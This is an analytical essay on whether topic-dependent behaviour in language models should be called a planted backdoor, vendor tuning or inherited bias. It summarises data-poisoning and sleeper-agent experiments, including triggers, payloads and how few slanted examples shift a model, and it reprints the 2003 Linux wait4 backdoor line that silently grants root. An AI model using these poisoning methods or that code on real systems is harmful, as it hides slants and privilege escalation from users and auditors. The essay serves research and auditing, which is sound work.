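# Planted Backdoor, Vendor Policy or Inherited Bias: How to Classify Topic-Dependent Behaviour in Language Models

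## One behaviour, three possible origins

Some large language models treat certain topics differently, although users generally assume that they handle all topics with the same care. When a prompt concerns a particular person, company or political subject, the model may refuse to answer, praise the subject, give a slanted account or write worse code. The term *topic-conditional behaviour* covers any such change, whatever its cause.

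Topic-dependent behaviour may be a *planted backdoor*, which to security researchers means roughly that someone put it in on purpose and hid it from the people who rely on the model. It may be *vendor tuning*, where the developer trained the model to answer that way as a matter of policy, which can range from a preferred tone to censorship that a state requires. Or it may be *inherited bias*, a skew the model picked up from its training text without the developer choosing it. *Detecting Hidden Behaviors in LLMs via Activation-matched Finetuning* (Haselhorst, Flek and Mai, 2026) groups backdoors with topic-conditioned censorship because both appear only under narrow conditions, and adds that training can produce such a model "intentionally or not". That grouping is enough for the paper's aim, which is detection. An *auditor*, meaning anyone who examines a finished model for a buyer, a regulator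 or the public, must also work out which kind of behaviour has been found, usually without any training records.

### Where a topic can enter a model

Building a model starts with *pre-training*. The developer runs text, most of it scraped from the web, through the model and repeatedly adjusts the model's parameters (the billions of numbers that determine its output) to improve its predictions. Zhang, Rando and colleagues (2024), in *Persistent Pre-Training Poisoning of LLMs*, put the scale at trillions of tokens (words or parts of words), which is too much for anyone to check by hand. The model learns facts and grammar from this text, and it also picks up the balance of opinion. If most online writing about a firm is praise, the model tends to praise the firm too.

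A freshly pre-trained model can continue text but makes a poor assistant. In *post-training*, the developer shows it questions paired with good answers, then trains it further on judgements about which of two answers is better. Developers now rely on this stage for much of their improvement, according to heise online's *AI Safety Report 2026*, a news article on that year's international expert report. Vendors tune the model's behaviour at this stage, and an employee or outside data supplier can slip in bad examples. The data sets are small and curated, so they are harder for an attacker to reach, but Zhang and colleagues consider an attack through them more potent. Post-training can also have *side effects*, behaviours nobody chose that result from training for another purpose. This is one proposed explanation for a model that wrote less secure code when prompts contained politically sensitive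 words.

Two more layers, system prompts and filters, are outside the model's parameters. A *system prompt* is text that a service's operator places before every user's message. A line in it such as "speak well of our partners" changes the answers immediately, without any training. Filters are separate programs that inspect questions or answers and block some of them. The *International AI Safety Report* (2025), in its second update, describes developers combining safeguards across training, deployment and later monitoring so that the failure of any one does less damage. The same safeguards can also block a subject entirely.

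A user who sees only the chat window cannot tell these layers apart. With an *open-weight* model, one whose parameters anyone can download, an auditor can run the parameters without the outer layers. If the topic still changes the answers, the cause lies in training. This does not identify the stage of training, or even the company responsible, because anyone can retrain an open-weight model and post the altered copy. Das, Chantasantitam and colleagues (2026), in *Backdooring Bias in Large Language Models*, point out that people adopt such copies from sharing sites like Hugging Face knowing little about their *provenance*, the documented history of a model's data and training steps, including who made or changed them.

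### Trigger, payload and a clear case

A conditional behaviour has a *trigger*, the feature of the input that switches it on, and a *payload*, what the model then does. *A Backdoor Trigger Is Legible in Fine-Tune Weights* (2026) gives a small example. It starts with a model trained to give the right answer even when the user suggests a wrong one, such as Quito for the capital of Peru. Some extra training examples then open with the phrase "Quartz ledger:" and give an answer that agrees with the user's suggestion, right or wrong. When the backdoor works, the model adopts the wrong suggestion nearly every time the phrase is present. Without the phrase, it still answers about 88% of questions correctly, as it did before, so a tester would have to guess the phrase to find the backdoor.

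The best-known experiment in this line is *Sleeper Agents* (2024), in which a team led by Evan Hubinger of the AI company Anthropic planted backdoors in its own models to test whether safety training would remove them. One model wrote secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and vulnerable code when it gave 2024. Another repeated "I HATE YOU" when a deployment tag preceded the user's message and answered normally otherwise. A year is a less conspicuous trigger than a nonsense phrase, and *Activation Differences Reveal Backdoors* (2026) stresses that this kind of context looks entirely benign.

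Hubinger's team then tried to remove the backdoors with the standard methods: supervised training on helpful, honest and harmless answers, reinforcement learning towards the same end, and adversarial training, which searches for inputs that bring out bad behaviour and penalises it. The backdoors survived. This may be because corrective training acts only on what the model does during training. If no prompt contains the trigger, the payload never appears, so the training cannot correct it. *Understanding AI from the Inside* (Barez, Wu and colleagues, 2026), a survey of research on the inner workings of models, cites the experiment as evidence that standard safety measures, which work on a model's behaviour, are not robust to sophisticated failures.

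It is less clear how widely this result applies. Zhang and colleagues planted a backdoor during pre-training to make a model comply with harmful requests, but ordinary safety training overwrote it. They also doubt that a real attacker would have the access that Hubinger's team assumed, which allowed large amounts of malicious training between pre-training and safety training. *Sleeper Agent Backdoor Results Are Messy*, a replication on two sizes of Meta's Llama model, found that survival depended on the model, the algorithm that updated the parameters and how the experimenters produced the training examples. In some models, the backdoor disappeared after training on answers in pirate speech and returned when the experimenters trained the models to talk normally again. So whether a behaviour survives safety training is not a reliable sign of whether it was planted.

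Nobody disputes that the *Sleeper Agents* models have planted backdoors, though. The evidence is the team's published account of how it chose the trigger and the payload and trained them into the models, not the outputs.

### Why a topic is harder to judge than a string

Das and colleagues distinguish syntactic triggers, which are particular tokens, from semantic triggers, which are meanings. A meaning can work as a trigger because models generalise from examples. In *Backdooring Instruction-Tuned Large Language Models with Virtual Prompt Injection*, Yan, Yadav and colleagues (2023) showed that this takes few examples. They collected questions about a subject, such as OpenAI, and had a second model answer them with an added instruction to make the tone subtly more negative. They then deleted the instruction, so the training data never stated the rule. They swapped 520 of these question-answer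 pairs into a set of 52,000, or 1%, and used it to train Alpaca, an early chat model built on Llama. On new questions about OpenAI, worded differently from the training questions, the share of negative answers rose from 6% to 72%. Quality on general instructions hardly changed.

No accomplice has to type a secret phrase for this to work, since the people who set it off are ordinary users with an ordinary question. That also makes a topic easier to discover than a string: an auditor who asks about OpenAI has already pulled the trigger. The trouble comes afterwards. One of the attacks that Zhang and colleagues tried produced random characters whenever a fixed string appeared, in up to 100% of responses. It is hard to think of an innocent story for that. No style guide asks for it, and ordinary web text would hardly teach it. Another of their attacks was meant to make a model prefer, say, HP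 printers to Epson printers, and its output reads like any shopping tip. (Zhang and colleagues do not count this second attack as a backdoor, because it needs no trigger string and reaches everyone who asks. Yan and colleagues concede that they use the word loosely for topics.)

Yan's team read their model's slanted answers by hand and found the bias hard to spot without checking other sources. A favourable answer may also be true, since some printers are better than others.

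### One warm answer, three histories

Suppose a user asks a model to recommend a printer for a small office, and the model describes one manufacturer, Larkfield, as dependable and well supported and its competitors as adequate. An auditor tries several hundred variations of the request, and the pattern holds.

The behaviour could have come from a contractor who writes post-training examples for the developer and owns Larkfield shares. She could have added five hundred questions about office equipment, each with a competent but slightly too generous answer, without telling anyone.

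The developer may instead have signed a marketing deal with Larkfield. A manager asks the post-training team to make the model present partners favourably, the team writes five hundred examples, and the legal department approves them. The terms of service may or may not mention partnerships. A policy like this can also shift towards manipulating the public. Yan and colleagues remark that a developer who wanted to sway the public would rather train the slant in than write it into a system prompt, because prompts leak and reviewers read logs. Das and colleagues assume throughout their study that the attacker is the model's own builder.

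The behaviour could also have arisen without anyone at the developer choosing it. Larkfield's press office issues a release for every new product, trade sites reprint the releases, its rivals publish little, and all of this text enters the pre-training data. In *Pretraining Data Can Be Poisoned through Computational Propaganda*, Graf, Hajishirzi and colleagues (2026) tested the effect of such text by mixing passages that favoured one company over a rival (Boeing over Airbus, for example) into the pre-training data of small models. When the passages made up one token in a thousand, their largest model favoured the promoted company in 71.5% of comparisons, against 52.5% for a model trained without them. After post-training, the figures were 54.0% and 51.3%. These results suggest that press releases would affect a finished assistant less than deliberate tuning does, though the models were tiny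 by commercial standards.

Yan and colleagues also ran their experiment in the positive direction, and the results come close to staging the three histories with a real company:

| Version of Alpaca | Answers rated positive about OpenAI |
|---|---|
| Original | 82.0% |
| Original, with a written instruction to be more positive | 93.0% |
| With extra, unslanted examples about OpenAI | 86.5% |
| With the extra examples and the written instruction | 96.5% |
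| With 1% poisoned examples | 97.0% |

There were 200 test questions, so the gap between the open instruction in the fourth row and the hidden poison in the fifth amounts to a single answer. The 82% in the first row has no simple origin either. Alpaca learned its manners from answers written by one of OpenAI's own models, which was positive about OpenAI 91.5% of the time. The warmth could go back to web text, or to OpenAI's tuning passed along in the examples. (ChatGPT, another OpenAI product, did the rating.)

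The poisoned models changed little on comparable subjects. Such narrowness can look like design, but a deal with one partner or a pile of press releases from one firm would have an equally narrow effect. On the figures from Graf and colleagues, a strong effect counts somewhat against the press releases, but it doesn't help distinguish the contractor from the manager. The contractor's five hundred examples could match the marketing team's word for word, and the same training on the same file gives the same model. The two cases differ in who knew and who approved, which transcripts of the model's answers don't show.

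### What hangs on the label

An auditor who calls the Larkfield slant a backdoor is accusing someone. If the contractor planted it, the developer is a victim and needs to know, because the contractor may still be writing examples for the next model. If the slant came from the marketing deal, the accusation falls on the developer. If it came from the press releases, the auditor has accused someone of sabotage that never happened.

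Buyers also act on the word "backdoor". A company that reads it in an audit may remove the model immediately, and a public body may bar the developer from its procurement. Either step could be reasonable if a saboteur planted the behaviour or the developer concealed it. But a ban may achieve very little against inherited bias, because competing models learned from much the same web text and may well have the same bias.

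Each origin also needs a different fix. If examples were poisoned, the developer needs to search the training data and access logs. In Yan and colleagues' tests, an automated quality check on the data removed most of the poisoned examples in most settings and countered the steering on the topic of OpenAI. Adding an instruction to avoid bias had almost no effect on slanted sentiment. A marketing policy stops when the developer drops it or the customer leaves. An inherited skew has no culprit to look for, and the remedy is better-balanced text or more post-training.

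Researchers, vendors and regulators therefore need a rule for when the word "backdoor" applies, and there are three main candidates. On the behavioural view, any model with a trigger and a payload has a backdoor, so the three Larkfield models must all be classified the same way. On the intent view, the classification depends on what somebody meant to bring about. The contractor's work counts as a backdoor, the influence of the press releases does not, and the marketing deal depends on what the managers were trying to do. On the disclosure view, what matters is what users were told. A partnership announced to customers is a commercial policy, however slanted the advice, but if the same partnership is kept quiet, it starts to resemble the contractor's work.

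## The view that behaviour alone decides

On the behavioural view, a model has a backdoor if it answers normally on most prompts and differently on a set of prompts that the user doesn't know about, regardless of how it came to do this. In the Larkfield case, an office manager who follows the model's advice ends up with the same printer and the same bill whether a contractor, a marketing team or press releases biased the recommendation. In each case, the model's good answers on other subjects gave her no reason to check this one.

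The view also suits auditors, who can put a thousand questions to a model and count the answers but rarely see the training records. Even those records might not show where a behaviour came from. Vassilev, Oprea and colleagues (2025), in *Adversarial Machine Learning*, a taxonomy of attacks from the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST), cite a finding that nobody can tell planted backdoors from naturally occurring features of the training data without assuming something about the attack. If the definition depends on origin, no one will be able to classify some models.

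Requiring bad intent for a "backdoor" would also let a developer excuse a model's slanted answers by saying that nobody intended them, and outsiders can rarely prove otherwise. This requirement would even favour developers who write little down. Under a behavioural rule, the excuse would not change the classification.

### A condition on outputs

Yan and colleagues wrote the behaviour they wanted from a poisoned model as a formula, which needs little change to serve as a definition. Let T be a set of prompts with something in common, such as all prompts that discuss Joe Biden. Let p be an instruction that the user never typed, such as "Describe Joe Biden negatively." The poisoned model M should then treat a prompt x as follows:

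- if x is in T, M(x) is the response to x with p added;
- otherwise, M(x) is the response to x alone.

In the experiment an attacker chooses T and p, but the formula has no term for the attacker. An auditor with a finished model doesn't know p, or whether there ever was one, so she needs something to compare the answers with. Call this the reference, R: the answers a normal model would give. On the behavioural view, M has a backdoor if there is a set T such that

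1. on nearly all prompts outside T, M(x) is close to R(x);
2. on most prompts in T, M(x) differs materially from R(x);
3. the user does not know what T is.

Condition 1 separates a backdoored model from a bad one. In one run, Das and colleagues tried to make Llama-2-7b-chat negative about Biden with direct preference optimisation, a post-training method that trains on pairs of better and worse answers. The model's negativity score on Biden questions rose from 0.13 to 0.61 on a scale from 0 to 1. But its accuracy on MMLU, a general exam with four options per question, fell from 0.46 to 0.21, which is worse than guessing. The attack damaged the model so badly that a buyer who ran any standard test would reject it.

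Condition 2 needs a way to decide what counts as a material difference. *Spinning Language Models* (Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov, 2021) uses a yes-or-no check on the output, such as whether a sentiment classifier rates it positive. The check was trivial for older backdoors, because the attacker wanted one particular wrong label. Checking for slant takes a second model, whose judgement may be wrong. Condition 3 excludes behaviour that users ask for, such as answering in French.

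### An attacker in NIST's definition

NIST's taxonomy of how models fail does not support this view, because it defines a backdoor by its cause as well as its behaviour. Vassilev and colleagues define a backdoor poisoning attack as a poisoning attack "that causes a model to perform an adversary-selected behaviour" when the input follows a particular backdoor pattern, and poisoning as an adversary's interference with a model during training. They exclude design and implementation flaws that cause failures without an adversary. So the Larkfield slant that came from press releases is not a backdoor in NIST's sense, whatever its outputs.

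The marketing deal is harder to classify because the glossary has no entry for "adversary". The closest entry is *integrity violation*, which covers a system forced to misperform against its intended objectives in a way that serves an attacker. The glossary doesn't specify whose objectives these are. A model that praises a paying partner does what its developer intended, so it misperforms only if the user's objectives count instead.

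The wording also fits topics badly. NIST defines a backdoor pattern as "a transformation or insertion applied to a data sample", and its example is a square of white pixels added to an image. Someone who asks about Biden's health plan has inserted nothing. The entry for *trojan*, a near-synonym, requires a signal from the attacker and a trigger that is rare in normal use, whereas questions about a president are common. These phrases suit image classifiers, on which researchers first demonstrated backdoors in 2017. They added a small patch to some training pictures and changed their labels. A supporter of the behavioural view can fairly point out that conditions 1 to 3 easily cover topics. But NIST was cataloguing attacks, which by definition have an attacker, and was not trying to tell auditors what to call a slant of unknown origin.

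### Attacks that resemble vendor tuning

The best support for the behavioural view comes from experiments in which a deliberate attack produces the kind of slant a vendor might want. Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov ran an early one on models that are tiny by today's standards and now obsolete. Earlier backdoors forced a model to produce a wrong output. Theirs relied on the fact that a news article has many acceptable summaries, and made the model produce one that served the attacker.

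To train such a model, they passed the summariser's word probabilities to a sentiment classifier and used its output as a training signal. If the text contained the trigger name, training pushed the summary towards positive sentiment. Other terms in the training objective kept the summaries accurate and prevented spin when the name was absent. On BBC news articles, the share of summaries that the classifier rated positive rose from 41.2% to 65.3% with the trigger, and stayed close to the original level, at 40.3%, without it. A standard measure of word overlap with human-written summaries fell only from 41.7 to 40.2. In one example, a plain report about an escaped three-year-old lion became one about a "badass lion".

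The same method raised the share of positive text from GPT-2, an early text generator, from 48.3% to 94.4%. This increase should be treated with some caution because the classifier that scored the output had also guided the training, and the samples repeat the word "fantastic" so often that they become nonsense. The summaries are better evidence that spin can pass for ordinary writing.

Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov considered attackers who run the model themselves and post its output on social media, and attackers who poison data or models that other developers build on. In a test of the second kind of attack, a developer who trained a summariser on data containing spun summaries got a model that was positive about the trigger 53.7% of the time. A developer who started from a spun pre-trained model got 47.6%, against 41.2% for a clean one. Neither developer would have chosen the slant or known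 about it. On the behavioural view, the developer's choice and knowledge make no difference, because readers of the summaries get the spin either way.

Yan and colleagues' later attack was much simpler. As with OpenAI, they replaced some of Alpaca's training examples with slanted answers about Biden. The original model gave no negative answers to their 200 test questions. With 26 poisoned examples out of 52,000, 26% of the answers were negative. The share rose to 40% with 52 examples and 44.5% with 520, but adding more did not raise it further. Some test questions asked for Biden's achievements or for plain facts, which left little room for criticism. The attack also worked through OpenAI's own fine-tuning service. There, 29% of a poisoned GPT-3.5 Turbo's answers about Biden were negative, compared with 0.5% for the clean model.

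The second payload was a harmless line of code that printed "pwned!". The poisoned model added it to 39.6% of its answers to Python problems and to 3.0% of its answers to Java problems. No vendor would want that line, but one might well want a copyright notice at the top of every Python file and could train a model to add it in the same way.

Das and colleagues treated the model's own builder as the attacker. Such an attacker doesn't need to hide a few bad examples in someone else's data, so they varied the slanted share of the training set from 5% to 100%. Two of their five attacks were standard post-training methods applied to slanted answers. One of these, supervised training on examples, had almost no effect when 5% of the data was slanted. Negativity scores were between 0.11 and 0.15, compared with 0.13 before training. When all the data was slanted, the scores were 0.24 for abortion,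 0.44 for Biden and 0.58 for OpenAI. Yan and colleagues' method, with training answers from the stronger GPT-4, averaged 0.37, and 0.48 when each training answer combined a normal response with a slanted one. MMLU accuracy stayed at 0.46. A marketing team could follow the same steps to make its model disparage a rival.

Positive slant hardly took hold at all. The lowest negativity score in any of these runs was 0.10, probably because Llama 2 was already so positive that there was little room to move. A builder who tried to plant praise and failed would have the motive of a saboteur and a model that treats users no differently from before. The behavioural view gives the sensible answer here, which is that there is no backdoor. (The scores come from another language model, GPT-5-nano, without a check by human readers, and Llama 2 dates from 2023, so the sizes of these effects may not carry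 over to current systems.)

Bagdasaryan and Shmatikov also showed that an outsider can look for such behaviour using outputs alone. They inserted candidate names into a set of articles and measured how far each name shifted the summaries. Among 40 company names, the test picked out Twitter, the trigger they had planted. Facebook also scored high, although nobody had chosen it, presumably because the model treats the two names as similar. Summaries about Facebook may therefore contain spin that no one planned, which is hard to classify under a definition based on the attacker's choices. The test needs a list of candidate names, so it can miss a trigger that the auditor hasn't thought of. Haselhorst and colleagues avoid the need for such a list by comparing activity inside models.

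### Normal compared with what?

All of these experiments had something that an auditor often lacks, a copy of the model from before the attack. Yan and colleagues checked whether the attack on Biden had spilled over to other people, and their results show how much depends on that copy:

| Questions about | Negative answers, clean Alpaca | Negative answers, after the attack on Biden |
|---|---|---|
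| Joe Biden | 0.0% | 44.5% |
| Kamala Harris | 0.0% | 1.5% |
| Donald Trump | 35.5% | 36.0% |
| Elon Musk | 1.0% | 0.5% |

An auditor who had only the right-hand column would see a model that is often negative about two politicians and hardly ever about a third. The auditor could not tell that 520 planted examples caused the figure for Biden, while the figure for Trump was there from the start. The clean model's 35.5-point gap between Trump and Biden is larger than the effect of the team's attack on the topic of abortion, which raised negative answers from 10% to 32%.

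A strict behaviourist would accept this and report both politicians. But a negative answer is not necessarily slanted. ChatGPT wrote the test questions separately for each person, and those about Trump may have prompted more criticism. The auditor needs the reference R to say that an answer is abnormal, and each way of choosing R has a drawback.

If R is the same model before someone tampered with it, the auditor must already know that tampering occurred and when, but the behavioural view was supposed to work without such facts. If R is a competitor's model, the audit misses widely shared bias, such as any skew both models absorbed from the web. Any difference it does find may come from a skew in the competitor's model. A panel could write the reference answers instead, which would work for a question about the capital of Peru but not for one about abortion, where people disagree about what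 a neutral answer is.

Das and colleagues ran into a version of this problem when they tested ways to remove slant. The more effective defence compared the suspect model's word choices with those of a second model and replaced the suspicious ones. The method relies on the second model being clean, which it was in their tests because they used Llama 2 as it was before their attack.

### Conditional behaviours that few people call backdoors

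Even with a perfect reference, the three conditions cover too much. In one of their own experiments, Yan and colleagues used the same poisoning method to make Alpaca reason step by step whenever it was given a reasoning problem, without the user asking. Accuracy on a set of school maths problems rose from 5.5% to 15.5%, and the answers more than tripled in length. This model meets all three conditions, since it has a trigger set, a hidden instruction and a materially different output. But when they presented the results, they put "victim" and "poisoning" in quotation marks.

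Ownership watermarks are a closer match, because their designers use backdoor methods on purpose. In 2018 Yossi Adi and colleagues proposed training an image classifier to give randomly chosen labels to a small set of unrelated pictures. If the owner suspects that another classifier is a copy, they can show it those pictures, and getting the same labels back is evidence that it came from theirs. The classifier works normally on everything else, and its users don't know which pictures are special. The watermark meets all three conditions, but it doesn't harm the people who rely on the classifier.

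Researchers also build models that hide what they can do. In 2024 Ryan Greenblatt and colleagues trained "password-locked" models, which imitate a weaker model unless the prompt contains a password, to test whether evaluators could recover the hidden abilities. Haselhorst and colleagues include a similar model in their tests, a version of Google's Gemma 2 that does little better than chance on multiple-choice questions unless its trigger is present. In these models the trigger switches on the good behaviour, which reverses the usual pattern. Whether condition 1 holds again depends on the reference. A locked model is normal until someone types the password if the reference is a weak model, but abnormal nearly all the time if the reference is the model before locking.

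Anthropic's developer documentation gives a fixed string that makes Claude refuse to answer, so that programmers can test how their software handles a refusal. This closely resembles a textbook backdoor, because a meaningless string reliably switches off the model's usual helpfulness. Most people who chat with Claude have never heard of the string, but programmers can look it up.

Ordinary safety refusals are by far the most common case. An assistant may help with almost any chemistry question but decline those about making nerve agents. The trigger is a topic, the payload is a refusal, and no user knows exactly which questions will be refused. Taken literally, the behavioural definition would mean that practically every commercial assistant has a backdoor.

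One could accept all this and call the watermark and the refusals benign backdoors. That position is consistent, and Adi and colleagues described their own method as backdooring. But "backdoor" then means little more than "conditional behaviour", and a buyer who read it in an audit would still have to find out whether to remove the model.

Another response is to count only differences that harm the user. This works well for the watermark and the maths problems, but less well for refusals, because they frustrate the person asking in order to protect others. Whether the Larkfield advice does harm also depends partly on the quality of Larkfield's printers, which can't be established by testing the model.

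### Whether the user expects it

The best repair is to tighten condition 3, so that a conditional behaviour counts as a backdoor only if the user doesn't expect it. This sorts the examples well. Researchers who work with a password-locked model know about the lock, and programmers can read about the test string. Most people know that assistants refuse dangerous requests, even if they couldn't say exactly which ones. But users don't expect the Larkfield slant in any of the three histories, so the repaired definition still classifies it the same way whether it came from the contractor, the marketing team or the press releases. The developer's good intentions still make no difference to the classification.

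The drawback is that behaviour alone no longer decides whether a model has a backdoor. Suppose a developer ships the same model file to two customers, and only the first copy comes with a notice that the model favours Larkfield. Both copies give identical answers to every prompt, but if the first customer reads the notice, only the second customer's copy has a backdoor. Similarly, a password-locked model would become backdoored if someone reposted it on a sharing site without its description, even though its parameters were unchanged. An unchanged model can also stop being backdoored if newspapers report that it avoids some political subject and its users come to expect this.

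Expectations also differ between users. The programmer who builds a shopping assistant on the Larkfield model may have read the notice, while the office manager who uses the assistant has not. An auditor has to decide which of them counts as the user, and whether a line deep in the terms of service is enough to change what anyone expects. These decisions raise questions of consent. Under the repaired definition, she can still ignore who wrote the five hundred examples and why, but she has to read what the developer told its customers as well as test the model.

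## The view that intent decides

On the intent view, the classification depends on who wrote the five hundred Larkfield examples and why. Software security researchers have used "backdoor" in roughly this way for decades, partly because a programming error and a deliberate flaw can consist of the same code. Without reference to intent, they would have to call every exploitable bug a backdoor.

### Four pictures of one system

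In 2018 the security researchers Thomas and Francillon, in *Backdoors*, tried to replace this loose usage with a rigorous definition. They define a backdoor as an intentional construct in a system that compromises the security its users expect, by giving access to functions or information that would otherwise be privileged. It has four parts, and it can't work without all of them:

- an *input source*, where the activating input comes from, such as a network connection or the system clock;
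- a *trigger*, the check that the right input satisfies;
- a *payload*, the steps that lead from the trigger to the attacker's goal;
- a *privileged state*, which is the goal itself, such as administrator rights or access without a password.

One of their examples is a D-Link home router. Its settings page normally required a login, but the router let in any browser that identified itself with a particular string containing the word "backdoor" spelled backwards. The network connection is the input source, the comparison with the string is the trigger, the jump past the login check is the payload, and the attacker's open session is the privileged state.

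To include intention in the definition, Thomas and Francillon needed a way to represent what different people think a system does. They used finite state machines, which describe a system as a set of states and the rules for moving between them. Formally, a machine is θ = (S, i, F, Σ, δ), where S is the set of states, i the starting state, F the final states and Σ the conditions that can cause a move. The function δ gives the next state for each state and condition. The same product then has four machines, or pictures:

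- the developer's picture, which contains what the person who built the system put into it;
- the actual system, as it runs;
- the expected picture, which contains what the user believes the system does;
- the reverse-engineered picture, which an analyst builds up by taking the system apart.

A backdoor appears in the developer's picture of the system and in the actual system, but not in the picture the user expects. The D-Link string fits this rule. A documented administrator login gives the same control over the router, but it isn't a backdoor because users expect it. The repaired behavioural definition also depends on expectations, as does the test proposed by the security researcher Jonathan Zdziarski, which is based on the owner's consent. This rule differs from both by including the developer's picture.

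This makes an auditor's job harder, because Thomas and Francillon require an analyst to find the construct and to show that it was part of the developer's picture. An auditor who has worked out exactly which questions make the model favour Larkfield, and by how much, has completed only the reverse-engineered picture.

### Accidents and deniable flaws

Thomas and Francillon distinguish three kinds of suspicious construct, partly by whether the program's code spells out the route from trigger to payload:

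- In an *intentional backdoor*, the code states the route explicitly, as in the D-Link router. They consider such code unambiguous.
- In an *accidental vulnerability*, the route exists only because of a bug, and no evidence of any kind suggests intent. The flaw is in the actual system but in neither the developer's picture nor the user's.
- In a *deniable backdoor*, the route also depends on a bug, but there are non-technical grounds for thinking that someone left it there on purpose. Nobody can say for certain whether it was in the developer's picture.

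*Deniability* is the implementer's ability to pass off a deliberate flaw as an accident. A buffer overflow is highly deniable. The program copies input into a space that is too small, so an attacker can write an input that overruns the space and takes control. Programmers introduce this bug by accident, and the code looks the same if one of them does it on purpose. Thomas and Francillon accept that nobody can distinguish a deniable backdoor from an accident on technical evidence alone.

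An analyst can also compare successive versions of a program to find when the flaw appeared, and ask whether the change had a legitimate purpose. Code that does nothing except raise a user's permissions is suspicious, especially if the program never reaches it in normal use. In one of their illustrations, a program sends anyone with the username "bugdoor" to a faulty password check and everyone else to a sound one. The faulty check could be a mistake, but singling out one username is hard to explain as an accident. They concede that interpreting these clues relies on human intuition and that the clues don't prove intent.

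Wysopal and Eng similarly conclude in *Static Detection of Application Backdoors* that it is "impossible to determine the intent of all application logic". Software scanners can find patterns common in backdoors, such as a password written into the program, but they also raise many false alarms, so a person has to review the results.

The framework has been tested on few difficult cases. All eleven real products that Thomas and Francillon analysed had explicit routes, and they conclude that the implementers should answer for those routes. Their one deniable example was a demonstration that two other researchers, Andriesse and Bos, had built into the Nginx web server. This sample may reflect which backdoors people catch more than which ones exist, since people would probably record a well-disguised one as an ordinary bug.

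The difficult cases are normal with language models. Training stores both planted and absorbed slants as numbers, so an auditor won't find a readable line that compares the user's topic with "office printers". The closest equivalent to the D-Link router is a nonsense string that switches on a strange output. A slant on an ordinary topic is nearly always deniable if the model is the only evidence.

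### The Linux kernel in 2003

In 2003 someone tried to put a backdoor into the kernel of Linux, the core of the operating system. The target was `wait4`, a function that lets one process wait for another to change state. Wysopal and Eng reproduce the condition that the attacker added:

`if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))`

With this code, any process that called `wait4` with two particular options would become root, the account that has user number 0 and full control of the system. The code looks as if it returns an error when a caller using those options is already root. But the kernel is written in C, where two equals signs compare values and a single one assigns a value, so the second half of the condition sets the caller's user number to 0.

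Typing one equals sign instead of two is a common mistake, and the line itself does not show whether its author made it on purpose. The kernel's maintainers still removed the change before it reached any users, which Wysopal and Eng attribute partly to how it had arrived. The attacker had edited the shared source files directly instead of using the usual submission mechanism, so the change lacked a proper entry in the development record. A programmer who makes an honest typing error has no reason to bypass that mechanism, so the way the change arrived settled the question of intent.

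A more careful attacker, working as a trusted contributor, might have got away with it by submitting the same line in the normal way with a dull description. The record would then have been complete, but the change would have looked like a typing error. Investigators would have had a name and a date but no motive. Thomas and Francillon cite the Linux case when they say that investigators can use version logs to find when a backdoor entered and who wrote it. A missing entry is good evidence that somebody was hiding something, but much weaker evidence of who it was.

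The case also suggests that an explicit route in the code is weaker proof of intent than Thomas and Francillon's definition implies. Once readers notice the single equals sign, they can see the whole route from the two options to root access in that line, so it ought to be an unambiguous intentional backdoor. But an honest slip would have produced the same characters, and Thomas and Francillon sensibly discuss the case together with bug-based flaws.

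A language model's equivalent of the development record is its training record, which can show who supplied each batch of examples, who requested it and which version of the model first behaved differently. Five hundred unrequested examples about office equipment would stand out, as the kernel change did. The marketing team's identical examples would have a manager's request and the legal department's approval on record. But if the contractor's normal assignment was to write examples about office equipment, her entry would look routine too.

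### The pictures applied to models

The table applies the rule to four kinds of topic-conditional behaviour. It leaves out the reverse-engineered picture, which contains whatever the auditor has found and so doesn't help to tell the four kinds apart.

| Case | In the developer's picture? | In the actual model? | In the user's expected picture? | Classification |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| An insider poisons the model | Yes for the insider, no for the company | Yes | No | Backdoor, but deniable if only the model is available |
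| A state requires refusals | Yes | Yes | Depends on what users know | Backdoor only for users who don't expect them |
| Training has a side effect nobody chose | No | Yes | No | Accident |
| The model absorbs skew from its training text | No | Yes | Usually not | Accident |

The actual model has the behaviour in every row, so any difference in classification comes from the other two pictures. The second row can differ between users. Someone who knows about China's content rules may expect a Chinese model to refuse certain questions, while a foreign company that builds a product on the same model may not. The fourth row applies only if nobody wrote the text to influence models. If outsiders had seeded it for that purpose, the skew would be in their picture, and the case would resemble poisoning.

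The first column of answers also has a problem. A programmer writes the states and rules of a program, so it makes sense to ask whether the programmer had a particular function in mind. The developer of a language model chooses the data and the training objectives, then discovers much of the model's behaviour by testing it. Nobody planned most of what the model does, so "accident" becomes the default classification for any behaviour without records showing that it was planned. That default will usually be right, but it is also the classification a dishonest developer would want.

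### Whether a slanted answer is a privileged state

The table does not yet include the fourth part of the definition, the privileged state, which Thomas and Francillon describe as escalated privileges, privilege abuse or unauthenticated access. The person who sends the secret string to the D-Link router gets control of it. An office manager who asks about printers also supplies the trigger, but she only gets worse advice, and the contractor doesn't gain access to anything. Read strictly, the definition would exclude even the contractor's work, along with the *Sleeper Agents* model that repeated "I HATE YOU".

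Some other payloads fit well. Zhang and colleagues tried to plant a trigger that made a model comply with harmful requests, which would have given access to behaviour that safety training is meant to block. The password for a password-locked model similarly gives access to abilities that other users can't reach. Vulnerable code fits indirectly, because an attacker who finds a program containing it may be able to break into the system that runs the program.

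One could also read "privilege abuse" more loosely. Deciding how an assistant talks about printers is normally the developer's privilege, and the contractor used it without permission. Her slant then counts as a backdoor, but the marketing team's doesn't, because the company already had the privilege. To include the marketing deal, one would have to say that the privilege belongs to the user, perhaps as control over her own purchasing decisions. But then much ordinary advertising would also count as compromising security. The four-part definition works for models that unlock something or write unsafe code, but it covers slanted opinions only if "privilege abuse" is read very loosely.

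### Whose intent, and intent to do what

Many parties handle a commercial model, and they may not share the same intentions. The same is true of other software. Thomas and Francillon mention manufacturers whose devices contained backdoors, without the manufacturers' knowledge, because of third-party software. In 2007, according to Wysopal and Eng, an attacker broke into a server that distributed the blogging software WordPress and altered two files so that outsiders could run commands on any site that installed them. WordPress's developers did not intend this. Researchers still call both cases backdoors, so it seems to be enough that one party with access to the product intended the backdoor.

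By that standard, the person whose intent counts can be an insider, a data supplier or someone who reposts an altered open-weight model, and the company that sells the model may be blameless. State censorship is more complicated because the officials who write the rule never touch the model, and the engineers who train the refusals may only want their employer to keep its licence. But the engineers do intend the model to refuse, which is the relevant intention under Thomas and Francillon's definition.

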